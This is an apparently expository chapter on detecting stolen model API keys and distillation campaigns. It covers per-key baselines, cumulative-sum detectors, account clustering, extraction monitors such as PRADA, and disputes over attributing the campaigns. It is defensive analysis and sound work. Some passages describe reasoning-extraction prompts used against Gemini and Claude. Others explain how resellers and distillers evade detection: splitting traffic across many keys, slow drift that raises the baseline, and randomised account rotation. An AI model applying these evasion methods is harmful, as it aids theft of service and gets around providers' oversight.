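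The security company Pillar set up honeypots (decoy servers) that imitated carelessly exposed model endpoints and MCP servers, and recorded 35,000 attack sessions between December 2025 and January 2026. Cohen and Fogel (2026), in *Operation Bizarre Bazaar*, put the average at 972 sessions a day. This is probably a little high, because it implies a period of 36 days, while a longer version of their report gives the period as over 40 days.

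Some of the traffic came from an operation that resold access to models. It tested endpoints two to eight hours, on average, after public internet scans had reached them. An owner who exposes a server by accident may therefore have only hours to notice. By late January, 60% of the traffic came from a separate campaign that probed MCP servers. Cohen and Fogel found no confirmed link between the two. They believe the second campaign was meant to reach the files and databases behind the servers. This is plausible, but probing alone can't confirm it.

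The total of 35,000 is the number of sessions, not intruders, and one busy scanner could account for thousands of them. It also doesn't show how many real companies lost anything. Pillar also sells protection against these attacks. Its evidence that people systematically search for exposed endpoints is still good, because nobody had a business reason to use the honeypots.

Honeypots also help defenders write new signatures. In the reseller's tests, Cohen and Fogel saw placeholder keys, which are dummy values from programming examples, such as `sk-test`. They advise alerting on these keys and on any address that tries several kinds of model software. A developer who forgets to replace a dummy key will trigger the first rule, so it works better on requests from outside the company. Cohen and Fogel also advise blocking a range of 256 addresses that the reseller used and, for the MCP campaign,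 all the address ranges of one network operator. Blocking a whole operator also blocks its legitimate customers, and an intruder can rent a server elsewhere.

A decoy works only if the intruder comes across it. In the Claude Mythos case, the contractor's colleagues already knew which model they wanted and had a way in, so Anthropic would probably have learned nothing about them from a planted key.

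## Detection of unusual use of a single credential

If someone steals the key for the shop's support chatbot and sends valid requests to a model the shop already uses, the requests may not match any signature. The owner can still compare the key's current use with its past use.

Detecting unusual use of a single credential requires a baseline for each key or service account, because company-wide totals can hide a change in one key's traffic. Suppose a company sends 50,000 requests an hour using 40 keys, and 200 of those requests use its chatbot's key. If a thief doubles the traffic on that key, the company's total rises by only 0.4%.

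To build the baseline, the owner calculates the usual level and spread of each measurement from several weeks of the key's log entries, preferably for each hour of the week, since 200 requests may be normal at noon but not at four in the morning. AWS (2025) similarly changed its detector for unusual spending to compare the latest 24 hours with equivalent periods from previous days, instead of comparing an unfinished day with complete ones.

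### What to measure

Volume features are the number of requests, the number of tokens, and their cost. All three are worth tracking because one can rise sharply while another barely changes. The chatbot's 200 requests an hour cost about $1.62 at the price calculated earlier. A thief who adds 30 requests at nearly $2 each, the cost per call in the Jet Night theft, raises the request count by 15% but multiplies the hourly cost by about 38. The count also has to include every kind of model call. AWS added a new kind called Converse in 2024, which CloudTrail logs under a different event name, and Sysdig saw attackers using it within 30 days.

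Context features describe a request's time, cloud region, network, client software and model. Shivam's *Attackers are hijacking company AI, using stolen access to run up bills* lists unusual models, unfamiliar regions and activity outside business hours among the warning signs. Most of these features are categories, so a detector checks how often the key has had that value before. If the chatbot runs on two servers, a single request from a third address deserves an alert, though the owner could simply block it. Unusual requests are harder to spot on a developer's key because its past use is more varied, and an intruder can also imitate the victim's network. Help Net Security describes an intruder who registered a domain that resembled one of the victim's internal hosts and used it to pass the company's model access to a resale operation.

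Content features include the language of a prompt, its topic, and its distance from past prompts. To measure that distance, a program first computes an embedding of each prompt, a list of numbers that a model produces from a text so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. For two embeddings *a* and *b*, a common choice is

distance = 1 − (*a* · *b*) / (|*a*| |*b*|)

This is 0 when the two lists point in the same direction and 1 when they are at right angles. The feature for a new prompt could be its distance from the nearest past prompt on the same key.

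The topic of prompts is probably a more useful sign of misuse than their language. In the stolen traffic that Sysdig studied in 2024, about 95% of the prompts were role-play, which would be very unusual for a shop's key but normal for a game company's. Of the roughly 4,800 prompts that remained after filtering, 80% were in English, so a language check at an English-speaking company would have missed most of them.

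If a key serves a single program, an even simpler check is whether each prompt begins with that program's standing instructions. Every legitimate prompt from the shop's chatbot does, and a thief who has only the key doesn't know the instructions.

### A score for one hour and a running total

The standardised score measures how far one count is from normal:

*z* = (*x* − *μ*) / *σ*

Here *x* is the count for the current hour, *μ* is the baseline's mean for that hour and *σ* is its standard deviation. The system sends an alert when *z* passes a fixed limit. Engineers who use the same formula to monitor factory production traditionally set the limit at 3. SigmaXL's *Average Run Length (ARL)* gives an average of one false alarm per 370 observations at that limit, assuming a normal distribution and counting deviations in both directions. With hourly counts, that is one about every 15 days for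 each key, or one every nine hours for a company with 40 keys. Raising the limit to 4 and counting only increases reduces this to about one a month for all 40 keys. Real traffic has more extreme hours than a normal distribution, so the true number will be higher.

The cumulative-sum detector, which E. S. Page introduced in 1954, carries evidence over from one hour to the next:

*S*ₜ = max(0, *S*ₜ₋₁ + *z*ₜ − *k*)

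The sum starts at 0, and the system sends an alert when the sum exceeds a limit *h*. Subtracting the allowance *k* every hour keeps ordinary variation from adding up. With *k* = 0.5 and *h* = 8, a standard approximation gives one false alarm per key in about two years of hourly counts, again under ideal conditions.

The standardised score is better at catching a sudden jump. A single hour at *z* = 6 exceeds the score's limit of 4 but adds only 5.5 to the cumulative sum. Bourazas (2026) explains in *Statistical Process Control* that the cumulative sum is better at catching a slow rise or a small, lasting increase. If a theft raises use by *δ* standard deviations every hour, the sum takes about *h* / (*δ* − *k*) hours to reach its limit. If *δ* is less than *k*, the sum keeps falling back towards zero and the theft can go on undetected indefinitely.

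Attackers have used stolen credentials both steadily and in sudden bursts. In 2024, Sysdig monitored attackers who made hundreds of requests a day for months, then 61,000 within three hours on 11 July. They made more than 85,000 requests in all.

### Three days on the chatbot's key

Suppose the chatbot's key averages 200 requests an hour during the working day, with a standard deviation of 20. Any count above 280 then gives a *z* above 4. The table covers eight hours of the key's use on each of three imaginary days: one with a burst of stolen use, one with a small, steady theft, and one on which the shop launches a product.

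| Hour | Burst: requests | Burst: *S* | Small theft: requests | Small theft: *S* | Launch: requests | Launch: *S* |
|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| 1 | 200 | 0 | 230 | 1.0 | 240 | 1.5 |
| 2 | 190 | 0 | 200 | 0.5 | 300 | 6.0 |
| 3 | 1,850 | 82.0 | 260 | 3.0 | 420 | 16.5 |
| 4 | 210 | 82.0 | 220 | 3.5 | 500 | 31.0 |
| 5 | 200 | 81.5 | 250 | 5.5 | 480 | 44.5 |
| 6 | 190 | 80.5 | 210 | 5.5 | 460 | 57.0 |
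| 7 | 210 | 80.5 | 240 | 7.0 | 440 | 68.5 |
| 8 | 200 | 80.0 | 250 | 9.0 | 420 | 79.0 |

The burst sets off both detectors in the third hour, when *z* is 82.5. The cumulative sum then stays above its limit for about six more days of normal traffic, so someone has to reset it after dealing with the alert.

On the day of the small theft, the highest count is 260, a *z* of 3, and the standardised score never raises an alert. The cumulative sum passes 8 in the eighth hour, by which time the key has been used for 260 more requests than usual.

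The launch triggers an alert from the standardised score in the second hour and from the cumulative sum in the third. Both alerts correctly detect traffic far above normal, but nobody has stolen anything. Raising the limits enough to ignore the launch would also hide any theft of the same size.

Message content can distinguish the two. Suppose that 1% of customers' messages normally lie more than 0.35 from the nearest past message, and that the shop sets an alert for any hour in which more than 5% do. In the busiest hour of the launch, customers send 500 messages. The product is new, but most of the messages ask about its price and delivery date, as past messages did about other products. If 15 of the 500 (3%) lie beyond 0.35, no alert goes out.

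In the first hour of the small theft, 200 of the 230 messages come from customers and 30 from a thief writing role-play. If 27 of the thief's messages and 2 of the customers' are distant, the distant share is 29 out of 230, or 12.6%. The content alert arrives seven hours before the cumulative sum reaches its limit.

These numbers were chosen to suit the example. A shop that starts selling insurance might trigger the content alert with legitimate questions, and a thief who wants product descriptions might not trigger it. The program also has to compute the embedding from the customer's message alone, because including the standing instructions would make all the chatbot's prompts look alike. The check requires access to the text of prompts, which raises the privacy problems described earlier. A simpler way to handle the launch itself is to tell whoever reads the alerts that it is happening.

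### A burst divided among 55 keys

Resellers can avoid large jumps in the use of any one key by spreading illicit use across many keys. Sysdig's *LLMjacking targets DeepSeek* (2025) describes one resale proxy that held 55 keys for DeepSeek, a Chinese model developer. According to Dark Reading's *LLM Hijackers Quickly Incorporate DeepSeek API Keys*, the operators pool keys partly because a large bill on any one account would raise alarms.

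The burst in the table contained 1,650 requests above the normal 200. Dividing the extra requests equally among 55 keys adds 30 to each. If every key has the same baseline as the chatbot's, each receives 230 requests, which gives a *z* of 1.5 and a cumulative sum of about 1. Neither detector raises an alert on any of the 55 keys.

If the reseller keeps up this rate, each key's cumulative sum grows by about 1 an hour and passes 8 in the ninth hour. With 200 keys, the extra use on each is only 8 requests an hour, or 0.4 standard deviations, which is below the allowance. A provider would have to link the accounts before it could add up use across the right 55 keys, which would give a *z* of about 11 for the burst, assuming the keys' normal variations are independent.

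Splitting the extra requests across keys hides the theft only if they cost about as much as the owners' own requests. Thirty requests at nearly $2 each would still stand out against every key's cost baseline.

Proxies may also spread their traffic less evenly than this. Sysdig captured statistics from another proxy, which had handled 132,651 prompts and 2.2 billion tokens in about four and a half days. The proxy listed 32 keys for OpenAI, two for Google, one for Azure and one for AWS, yet Claude models on AWS accounted for two-thirds of the tokens. Some AWS keys may have dropped off the list by then. But if one key carried all the Claude traffic, its owner was paying around $350 an hour for Claude 3 Opus alone, by Sysdig's estimate. A reseller needs many keys for the same model to hide heavy use of it.

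### What each hour of delay costs

The direct loss from a theft is simple to calculate:

loss = cost per hour × hours until someone revokes the key

| Theft | Revoked after 1 hour | After 12 hours | After 24 hours |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| 30 cheap chatbot-sized requests an hour | $0.24 | $2.92 | $5.83 |
| All the keys in the second Sysdig proxy, at about $451 an hour | $451 | $5,400 | $10,800 |
| A theft costing $100,000 a day | $4,200 | $50,000 | $100,000 |

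A slow detector is good enough for the first theft, at least financially. For the others, most of the loss depends on how quickly the alert arrives, and billing alerts arrive late.

AWS's detector for unusual spending runs about three times a day on data that can be 24 hours old, so AWS warns that an alert can arrive up to 24 hours after the use that triggered it. The detector also needs ten days of history before it can detect unusual spending on a service that is new to the customer. In several of Mandiant's cases, the intruders switched on AI services that had been off and so would have had no such history.

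A bigger gap is that the detector doesn't monitor third-party products sold through AWS's marketplace, which AWS says include Anthropic's Claude models on Bedrock. Under the current rules, it would miss most of the spending in the second Sysdig proxy.

For those charges, AWS recommends its budget tool, which sends an alert when spending passes a fixed amount. AWS typically updates the budget figures every 8 to 12 hours, and the theft that supplied Jet Night lasted less than eight hours. AWS also says that costs may pass the threshold before the alert goes out.

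Crystal Morin of Sysdig told Dark Reading about a man who used his AWS account mainly for email and paid about $2 a month. He woke one morning to find that the bill had reached $730 within two or three hours. He had turned on cost alerts, which are off by default, and he closed the account almost immediately. Because the cost reports lagged, the final total was still between $10,000 and $20,000 for about half a day's use. At the rate he first saw, half a day would have cost less than $4,500. AWS eventually covered the loss.

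An owner who records token counts can calculate the cost before the bill arrives by multiplying each hour's tokens by the model's price. This figure is the most useful input to the two detectors because it can be ready within minutes and reflects both heavy use and the use of expensive models. It is available only if the owner has switched on the log that records token counts.

A hard spending limit caps the loss even if nobody notices the theft. In IT Brew, Morin suggests price and activity limits, though a limit low enough to stop a thief might also stop the chatbot during a launch. In the same article, Dan Moore of the identity company FusionAuth recommends short-lived credentials. A key that expires after an hour limits the hours in the formula, unless the thief can obtain a new one.

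### Baselines that are out of date or missing

Normal use changes over time, which is known as drift. *ServeGen* (2025) measured production model traffic in five-minute windows and found that the rate and burstiness of requests shifted in different ways for different workloads. A baseline that is months old may therefore cause frequent false alerts.

The usual remedy is to recalculate the baseline from recent data, but a thief who increases their use slowly can then raise the baseline too. Suppose the detector compares each day with the average of the previous seven, and a thief increases the key's total traffic by 1% a day. Each day is then about 4% above the average. On the chatbot's key, the difference starts at 8 requests an hour, or 0.4 standard deviations. The cumulative sum doesn't build up, at least as long as the measured spread grows with the traffic, and after 70 days the key is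 sending twice as many requests as before. Keeping a fixed copy of an old baseline as well would reveal the doubling, and somebody could then ask the owner whether the business had grown that much. The owner should also exclude any hours found to include theft from the recalculation.

A new key has no baseline, so the detector can use one from similar keys, or the person who creates the key can declare its intended use, such as one model, certain servers and at most 500 requests an hour. The declaration works from the first request and can be much stricter than a statistical limit. To catch intruders who keep creating and deleting service accounts, the owner should also keep a baseline for the whole cloud account, because every request adds to the account's total whichever service account sends it. No single short-lived credential lasts long enough to have a history, so the history should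 be kept for the program or person that receives the credentials.

Unusual use is harder still to detect when the credential belongs to an agent. *TraceLab* (2026), a study of coding agents, describes sessions in which tools trigger frequent model calls, with gaps while the agent waits for a person. Suppose a developer's agent sends 400 requests in one hour out of ten and none in the rest. Its mean is 40 requests an hour and its standard deviation is 120, so the limit at *z* = 4 is 520. A thief could send 400 requests in any idle hour without exceeding the limit. The cumulative sum would detect four such hours in a row, but it would also raise an alert whenever the developer worked with the agent for four hours.

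Requests per hour is a poor measure for an agent that runs on a developer's machine. It makes more sense to measure requests or cost per task, and to check that each batch of requests matches a session that a logged-in person started. A thief may send a normal number of requests, but they won't match a session on the developer's machine. This check works only if the gateway or the agent program records sessions, and many deployments don't record them.

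### Language models as judges of login records

A language model could read a summary of a key's activity and judge whether it looks wrong. Henshaw and Karmakar (2026), in *From Noise to Signal*, tested this idea on a related problem, remote logins to a Linux computer over the SSH protocol. They compared three language models with Wazuh, a security tool that matches events against written rules, and with OpenSearch's anomaly detector, which looks for statistical changes in a stream of numbers.

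The researchers set up one virtual machine to monitor and another to attack it. They prepared 75 scenarios from hundreds of login events and rated each one's severity from 0 to 5. They counted the 51 scenarios rated 2 or above as anomalies and the other 24 as normal. Twenty of the anomalies were borderline cases rated 2, such as several failed logins followed by a successful one from the same address.

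| Detector | Anomalies caught, of 51 | Borderline anomalies caught, of 20 | False alarms, of 24 |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 45 | 16 | 2 |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 35 | 11 | 1 |
| GPT-OSS 20B | 16 | 5 | 0 |
| Wazuh | 16 | 4 | 1 |
| OpenSearch | 13 | 3 | 0 |

GPT-OSS did badly mainly because only 22 of its 75 answers were in the required format. Of those 22, 21 were correct. Two further runs produced 29 valid answers each. All three models are small by current standards, and Llama 3.1 dates from 2024, so newer models might well do better.

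The comparison was far from equal, however. Wazuh and OpenSearch worked from log events and numbers derived from them, while the language models received a written description of each scenario. A description that mentions failed logins followed by a success from the same address already identifies much of the suspicious pattern. The models' instructions also listed seven signs to look for, including very regular timing and activity without rest periods, and the researchers had used similar characteristics to assign the severities. Henshaw and Karmakar accept that the experiment doesn't prove that the models' grasp of meaning caused the improvement. They recommend using language models alongside the existing tools.

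The false-alarm figures are also very uncertain. Two false alarms in 24 normal scenarios are compatible with a true rate from 1% to 27%. This uncertainty matters more when real intrusions are rare, because false alarms then make up a larger share of alerts.

Less of this carries over to model endpoints than the table might suggest. The Wazuh rule that fired most often, 644 times, detects attempts to log in as a user who doesn't exist. A thief with a working key doesn't need to guess, so there may be no failed attempts to detect. Several of the seven signs distinguish a program from a person, but the legitimate user of a model key is often a program, such as the shop's chatbot, which runs all night without pausing. A language model with the same instructions might flag the chatbot and miss a thief who sends a few requests by hand in the afternoon.

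A language model is more promising as a second step, used only when the cumulative sum passes its limit. It could then read the hour's prompts and report that 30 of them are role-play unrelated to the shop's orders. Llama took 1.86 seconds per scenario, which is fast enough for a few alerts a day but would be a heavy load for 200 requests an hour across thousands of keys. The experiment didn't test this arrangement.

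### Tests on real usage logs

No public study appears to have tested a detector of stolen keys on real model-usage logs, but such logs are becoming easier to get. *BurstGPT* (2024) released 213 days of traffic from Microsoft's Azure OpenAI service, with the time, model and token counts of each request. *FineServe* (2026) covers many models on a commercial marketplace. The trace in *A Year in LLM Serving* (2026) is probably the largest, with 6.12 billion requests to 9,174 models over a year. It keeps an anonymised identifier for each user, so a researcher could build a baseline for each one.

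Engineers published these datasets to help plan computing capacity, and the datasets' descriptions don't mention labels identifying thefts. Without such labels, researchers can't calculate recall. They could still run both detectors on the year-long trace and count the alerts per user, which would estimate the false-positive rate far better than a normal distribution does, although some alerts might be real thefts that nobody noticed at the time. To estimate recall, they could add artificial thefts to the trace, but the estimate's accuracy would depend on how closely these resembled real ones.

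## Detection of coordinated use across many accounts

When a reseller splits a burst of requests across 55 keys, the volume on each key looks ordinary, so a provider can catch the reseller only by working out which accounts belong together.

Some exchanges look innocent until an analyst compares them with thousands of others. Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026) describes a studio in China that ran more than 20 dating apps and used Claude to play most of the "people" on them. Over two weeks in April 2026, more than 4,700 personas talked to at least 25,000 users. The instructions to Claude read like those of an ordinary role-play app, and Anthropic found that no single exchange revealed the deception. The studio reached Claude through many throwaway accounts, most tied to Chinese resale proxies. Anthropic often catches such accounts by finding the proxy network.

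### Distillation campaigns

The largest known cases involve distillation, in which a developer trains a "student" model on the answers of a stronger "teacher". Companies routinely do this with their own models to make smaller, cheaper versions. A rival can do it through an ordinary model endpoint if it collects enough answers before the provider stops it.

On 23 February 2026, Anthropic accused three Chinese companies of using fraudulent accounts to distil Claude. Its *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) attributes over 16 million exchanges, through about 24,000 such accounts, to the companies' three campaigns. It attributes over 13 million of the exchanges to MiniMax, over 3.4 million to Moonshot AI and over 150,000 to DeepSeek.

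The 16 million exchanges were spread across 24,000 accounts, or about 670 per account. MSSP Alert put one person's normal use at 500 to 1,000 calls a day, so the average account did no more in the whole campaign than one person might do in a day. A limit low enough to stop the average account would also stop ordinary customers.

Usage per account varied widely around this average, though. Moonshot used "hundreds" of accounts, so even if there were 999, they would have averaged 3,400 exchanges each. One proxy network ran more than 20,000 accounts at once and mixed distillation requests with those of unrelated customers. Its accounts therefore carried more traffic, with more varied prompts, than the attributed exchanges alone.

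Anthropic names several signs that tied accounts together. DeepSeek's accounts shared payment methods and sent traffic in identical patterns at coordinated times. Anthropic traced request metadata to particular researchers at DeepSeek and matched it to the public profiles of senior Moonshot staff. The prompts had repetitive structures and focused narrowly on skills such as coding, tool use and step-by-step reasoning. A typical one asked Claude to act as an expert data analyst and back its conclusions with complete reasoning. One such prompt would be unremarkable, but Anthropic saw variations of them tens of thousands of times across hundreds of accounts. MiniMax's accounts also reacted together when Anthropic released a new model, moving nearly half the campaign's traffic to it within 24 hours.

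Eleven days earlier, Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) had described over 100,000 prompts that tried to make Google's Gemini model print its full reasoning instead of the usual summary. One instruction told Gemini to think in the user's language. Google inferred from the breadth of the questions that someone wanted to copy Gemini's reasoning in languages other than English. Google says its systems recognised the attack in real time, which is plausible because a fixed, unusual instruction is easy to match. It didn't say how many accounts sent the prompts, so detecting the campaign may not have required linking accounts.

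Later campaigns were larger. Music Business Worldwide's *Anthropic, fighting lawsuits over alleged copying of song lyrics, accuses Alibaba* reports a letter of 10 June in which Anthropic attributed 28.8 million exchanges to operators affiliated with Alibaba. By September, Anthropic had raised that count to 151 million exchanges for the period from May to July, and had identified campaigns by seven Chinese labs since February. The last column below divides the published totals by accounts and days.

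| Campaign, according to Anthropic | Exchanges | Accounts | Days | Per account per day |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Alibaba, 22 April to 5 June | 28.8 million | 25,000 | 45 | 26 |
| Alibaba, busiest day | 3 million | 3,500 | 1 | 860 |
| Zhipu, extraction of reasoning | 770,609 | 273 | 10 | 280 |
| Xiaomi | 400,000 | 1,500 | 20 | 13 |
| Moonshot, relayed customer requests | 300,000 | 5,380 | 10 | 6 |

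Only Alibaba's busiest day comes anywhere near a volume that would look odd for one person. (The Zhipu figure assumes that all the counted exchanges went through the 273 accounts.)

Moonshot's traffic is the hardest to spot, partly because its volume is low and partly because, according to Anthropic, the prompts came from real people with unrelated problems. Anthropic says that Moonshot silently forwarded its own customers' requests to Claude, returned the answers as if its Kimi model had written them, and kept at least some of them for training.

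### From shared details to clusters

Anthropic describes its detectors only in outline, but investigators have long used the same general method to find fake accounts on social networks. They build a graph in which each account is a point and a link joins any two accounts that have something in common.

The provider starts with details such as payment cards, network addresses and sign-up records. A rare detail is stronger evidence than a common one, so each link needs a weight. A simple choice is

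*w* = log₁₀(*N* / *n*)

where *N* is the number of accounts on the service and *n* is the number that share the detail. On a service with a million accounts, a card that pays for two of them has a weight of 5.7. The address of a mobile phone network, which 10,000 accounts share, has a weight of 2.

Next, for each pair of accounts, the provider finds the share of prompts in one that closely match a prompt in the other, and multiplies that share by 5 so that it counts about as much as a shared card. It adds the two scores and discards every link whose total is below a chosen limit. Accounts that remain connected, directly or through other accounts, form a cluster.

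Suppose there are six accounts, A to F. A and B use the same card. B and C connect from the same rented server, which 100 accounts use. D, E and F each have their own card and connect through a mobile network. Any two of A, B, C and D have 80% of their prompts in common, and every other pair has 10%.

| Pairs | Shared detail | Weight | Prompt score | Total |
|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
| A–B | Payment card | 5.7 | 4.0 | 9.7 |
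| B–C | Rented server | 4.0 | 4.0 | 8.0 |
| A–C, A–D, B–D, C–D | None | 0 | 4.0 | 4.0 |
| D–E, D–F, E–F | Mobile network | 2.0 | 0.5 | 2.5 |
| The other six pairs | None | 0 | 0.5 | 0.5 |

With a limit of 3.5, A, B, C and D form a cluster, and E and F stay separate. D would have stayed out of the cluster without the comparison of prompts, because the only other thing it shares with any account is a phone network. If every shared detail had a weight of 4, D's links to E and F would pass the limit and all six accounts would form one cluster.

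The last step is to judge the cluster as if it were one customer. Suppose four accounts each send 600 requests a week, or 2,400 in total, and 90% of those ask for worked solutions to data-analysis problems, compared with 3% of requests on the whole service. An analyst should review a cluster with such a narrow focus, but four data analysts at a small firm who share a company card and a prompt template could produce the same one.

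A real campaign would have thousands of accounts, which makes detection harder. A million accounts make about 500 billion pairs, so the provider has to look up which accounts share a detail instead of comparing every pair. A single misleading link can also merge two large groups. For example, if a resale proxy uses a stolen key, the rightful owner's account joins the cluster, and a provider that banned the whole cluster would also ban the victim of the theft.

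Accounts can also be linked indirectly. When Anthropic banned a first pool of nearly 5,000 accounts that it connected to Alibaba, the traffic quickly moved to a second pool. A sudden fall in one group's traffic and a matching rise in another's is good evidence that the same customer is behind both. But some accounts in the second pool also carried requests from DeepSeek and Xiaomi. Payment and network details had led to the proxy service, but separating its customers requires examining their prompts.

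### What rewording does to a match

Near-duplicate matching is one of two common ways to decide whether prompts match. It breaks each prompt into short overlapping runs of words. The similarity score for two prompts is the number of runs they share divided by the total number of distinct runs in the pair. The score is 1 for identical texts and 0 for texts with no run in common.

The prompt "Solve this problem and show every step of your reasoning" contains nine pairs of adjacent words. Changing "problem" to "puzzle" alters two of them, so the two versions share seven of the eleven distinct pairs between them and score 0.64. "Work through the question, explaining how you reach each conclusion" is much the same request but shares no pairs with the original, so it scores 0.

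Near-duplicate matching takes little compute because a technique called MinHash can estimate the similarity score of two prompts from a short list of numbers for each. The matching works well against a campaign that keeps part of its prompt fixed. According to Anthropic, Alibaba's system added the same text to every request to make Claude write out its reasoning. That text would link the accounts whatever question followed, but the provider has to match it separately because long, varied questions would otherwise lower the score.

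Embedding similarity compares the meanings of prompts instead of their words, so a reworded prompt should remain close to the original. This makes rewording a poor way for an attacker to avoid detection, but the method also groups together prompts from honest customers who want the same thing, such as a thousand students asking about the same homework problem.

One lab, which Anthropic doesn't name, tested over 12,000 requests, each with a different technique for extracting Claude's reasoning, and then used the successful techniques in a larger campaign. Near-duplicate matching might find little in common among the test requests. Comparing their embeddings would be more likely to link them, since they all had the same aim, though a long passage added as disguise could move a prompt's embedding away from the others.

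Neither method helps much with relayed customer requests, which differ in wording and meaning. To detect these, the provider has to rely mostly on payment, network and timing data, or on signs that the relay adds to the requests.

### PRADA and what came after it

Researchers were trying to detect model copying before chatbots were common. *PRADA* (2018) was designed for models that classify images. It measures the distance between each new image from a client and the nearest earlier image that the model put in the same class. PRADA assumes that an ordinary client's distances follow a normal distribution, or bell curve. Many attackers of the time made artificial images by altering earlier ones in regular steps, which distorts the curve. PRADA raises an alert when the distances are too far from a normal distribution, so it doesn't need a description of the particular attack.

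Its inventors also tested how an attacker could evade it. One attack on a model that recognises traffic signs needed 41,160 dummy queries to restore the bell curve and hide its 6,680 useful ones. Having to send about seven times as many queries deters theft but does not prevent it. The inventors also acknowledged that what counts as a normal distribution depends on how people use the model.

Later attacks evaded PRADA without dummy queries. *ES Attack* (2020) generated 300,000 images to attack a model of handwritten digits, and PRADA flagged none of them. PRADA also responded too slowly to be practical for a provider. *D-ADD* (2025) found that PRADA suits attacks that mix real images with altered copies, but misses attacks such as KnockoffNets, which sends the model ordinary pictures from an unrelated collection. Copying a model doesn't require the regular steps that one generation of attacks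 used.

PRADA also keeps a separate record for each client, so, like any limit on a single account, it can miss an attack spread across many accounts. *The Limits of Query Monitoring against Distributed Model Extraction* (2026) tested monitoring across accounts. The simulated attackers divided their prompts among many accounts whose volume matched ordinary users'. On held-out data, the monitor caught campaigns with dataset-like prompts in 86 to 100% of weeks, with about 2% false alarms. Per-account monitors caught essentially none, although the researchers tested those on the weeks they had used for development.

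If the 2% false-alarm rate is per clean week, one monitor would raise about one false alarm a year. That is an excellent result, but it applies to prompts that resemble a training dataset. The paper describes the monitor as a filter rather than a complete defence, because it detects a coordinated shift in topic. It cannot distinguish a distiller from a customer who benchmarks a model using ten accounts.

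*Fingerprinting the Dispatchers behind Distributed Model Extraction* (2026) focuses on the dispatcher, the software that shares out requests among accounts. It cites an open-source gateway that can use its keys in strict rotation. This leaves a trace because the accounts' request counts are too similar. If independent accounts average 100 requests a day, chance alone would give a standard deviation of about 10, and real customers vary far more than that. Under strict rotation, no two accounts differ by more than one request. Rewording the prompts or relaying other people's questions doesn't remove this trace. Choosing the accounts at random would remove most of it, although their request counts would still be more alike than those of real customers.

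### Innocent clusters and missing ones

University students could produce most of the signs in the six-account example. They share a network, some of their accounts may share a payment method, and a class with an assignment due on Friday sends similar prompts at similar times. Permitted resellers and services that route requests to several models also send many unrelated people's requests through a few accounts. Rarity weights help with large shared networks but do little for a laboratory where ten people share one card.

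A cluster is therefore a reason to investigate. Anthropic can require users of suspicious accounts to verify their identity, and bans accounts that fail. This is fairer than banning everyone at once, but it inconveniences honest users and won't always catch people who already open accounts under false identities. A provider could register universities and permitted resellers in advance, so that an analyst who finds a cluster of their accounts knows whom to contact.

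The NSA, CISA and FBI, in their September advisory *China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns* (2026), also recommend monitoring each subscription's usage relative to its price, new accounts that immediately reach maximum use, and throughput on the scale of a large company. These signs can distinguish a distiller from a class of students, because few students exhaust a premium subscription from the first day. They would be less useful against a campaign that sends six requests per account per day.

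The agencies also warn that the companies spread their requests over several providers and switch automatically when one blocks them. Anthropic describes a case in which Zhipu collected solutions to hacking exercises from another American lab's model and used Claude mainly to grade them. Anthropic's logs alone would have recorded the grading but not the extraction of the answers, which would have concealed the purpose. Music Business Worldwide, citing Bloomberg, reports that Anthropic, OpenAI and Google have agreed to share information about distillation attempts. Anthropic believes antitrust rules make such sharing harder.

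Sharing information would not reveal a lab that sends no requests itself. Anthropic says SenseTime bought transcripts of other people's conversations with Claude from data vendors, which had obtained them from services that logged their users' exchanges. Those users made the requests for their own purposes, so the traffic contained no distillation campaign to detect.

### Who is behind a cluster

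Showing that accounts act together is easier than showing who controls them. Anthropic attributed the campaigns it disclosed in February with "high confidence", using network addresses, request metadata and, in some cases, corroboration from other companies. It also compared the timing of MiniMax's requests with MiniMax's public product plans, which is weaker evidence because a match could be a coincidence. Outsiders can't examine the metadata, so they have to take the attributions largely on trust. Publishing it would expose customers' data and show the operators of future campaigns what to hide.

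Anthropic also has an interest in the matter, though that doesn't make the findings false. Semafor's *Anthropic accuses Chinese firms of distillation attacks* (2026) notes that Anthropic has consistently favoured export restrictions to slow China's AI progress, and its February post presents the campaigns as a further reason for them. OpenAI, which competes with the same firms, made a similar accusation against DeepSeek and others in a memo to a congressional committee that month, according to The Tech Portal's *Anthropic says Chinese AI firms, including DeepSeek, 'distilled' Claude* (2026).

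The American government has backed the American labs. Axios' *U.S. accuses China of "industrial-scale" campaigns to steal AI secrets* (2026) reports that in April the White House accused mostly China-based actors of using proxy accounts to extract capabilities from American models. The September advisory names six companies: DeepSeek, Moonshot, Alibaba, MiniMax, StepFun and Z.AI (Zhipu's name outside China). It is unclear how much of the agencies' evidence came from the labs themselves, which weakens this support.

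The advisory's timeline also conflicts with public release dates. NSA, CISA and FBI list GPT-5 among the models that DeepSeek distilled between late 2024 and mid-2025 to train its R1 and V3 models, but OpenAI released GPT-5 in August 2025, months after R1 came out. The agencies may have meant later versions of DeepSeek's models, but GPT-5 can't have contributed to the original R1.

The accused companies have said little. DeepSeek, Moonshot and MiniMax hadn't responded publicly or to journalists when TechInformed covered the February accusations. Alibaba hadn't answered the Global Times, a Chinese state-run newspaper, by 25 June. The Chinese embassy called the White House's claims "pure slander", according to PC Gamer.

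The fullest reply comes from Tian Feng, a former head of a SenseTime research institute, who was outside the firms accused at the time. Chen and Zhang (2026) quote him in *Anthropic's 'distillation' claims against Chinese firm lack substance*. He calls distillation a widely adopted technique and attributes the accusations to anxiety about losing technological dominance. Anthropic agrees that the technique is legitimate in itself, so his first point doesn't settle the main dispute, which is over who may use Claude's answers to distil models and whether these companies did.

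The published evidence that accounts were coordinated is more convincing than the evidence for some of the labs named as responsible. Thousands of accounts that share payment methods and have the same unusual text in their prompts are hard to explain without coordination. But several labs can use the same proxy network, so an investigator could easily attribute one lab's requests to another.

### When distillation is unauthorised

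Whether distillation is authorised depends on the provider's terms, as with resale. Google offers its own distillation services, but distilling Gemini without permission breaks Google's terms of service. Authorised and unauthorised distillation could use identical prompts.

The February cases are simpler than this suggests, because Anthropic doesn't offer commercial access to Claude in China or to Chinese companies' subsidiaries abroad. If the attributions are right, the users were unauthorised whatever their purpose. Purpose matters more in Google's cases. Google Threat Intelligence Group observed companies and researchers worldwide attempting extraction, and says the method uses legitimate access. Some of them may have been customers in good standing whose only breach was their intended use of the answers.

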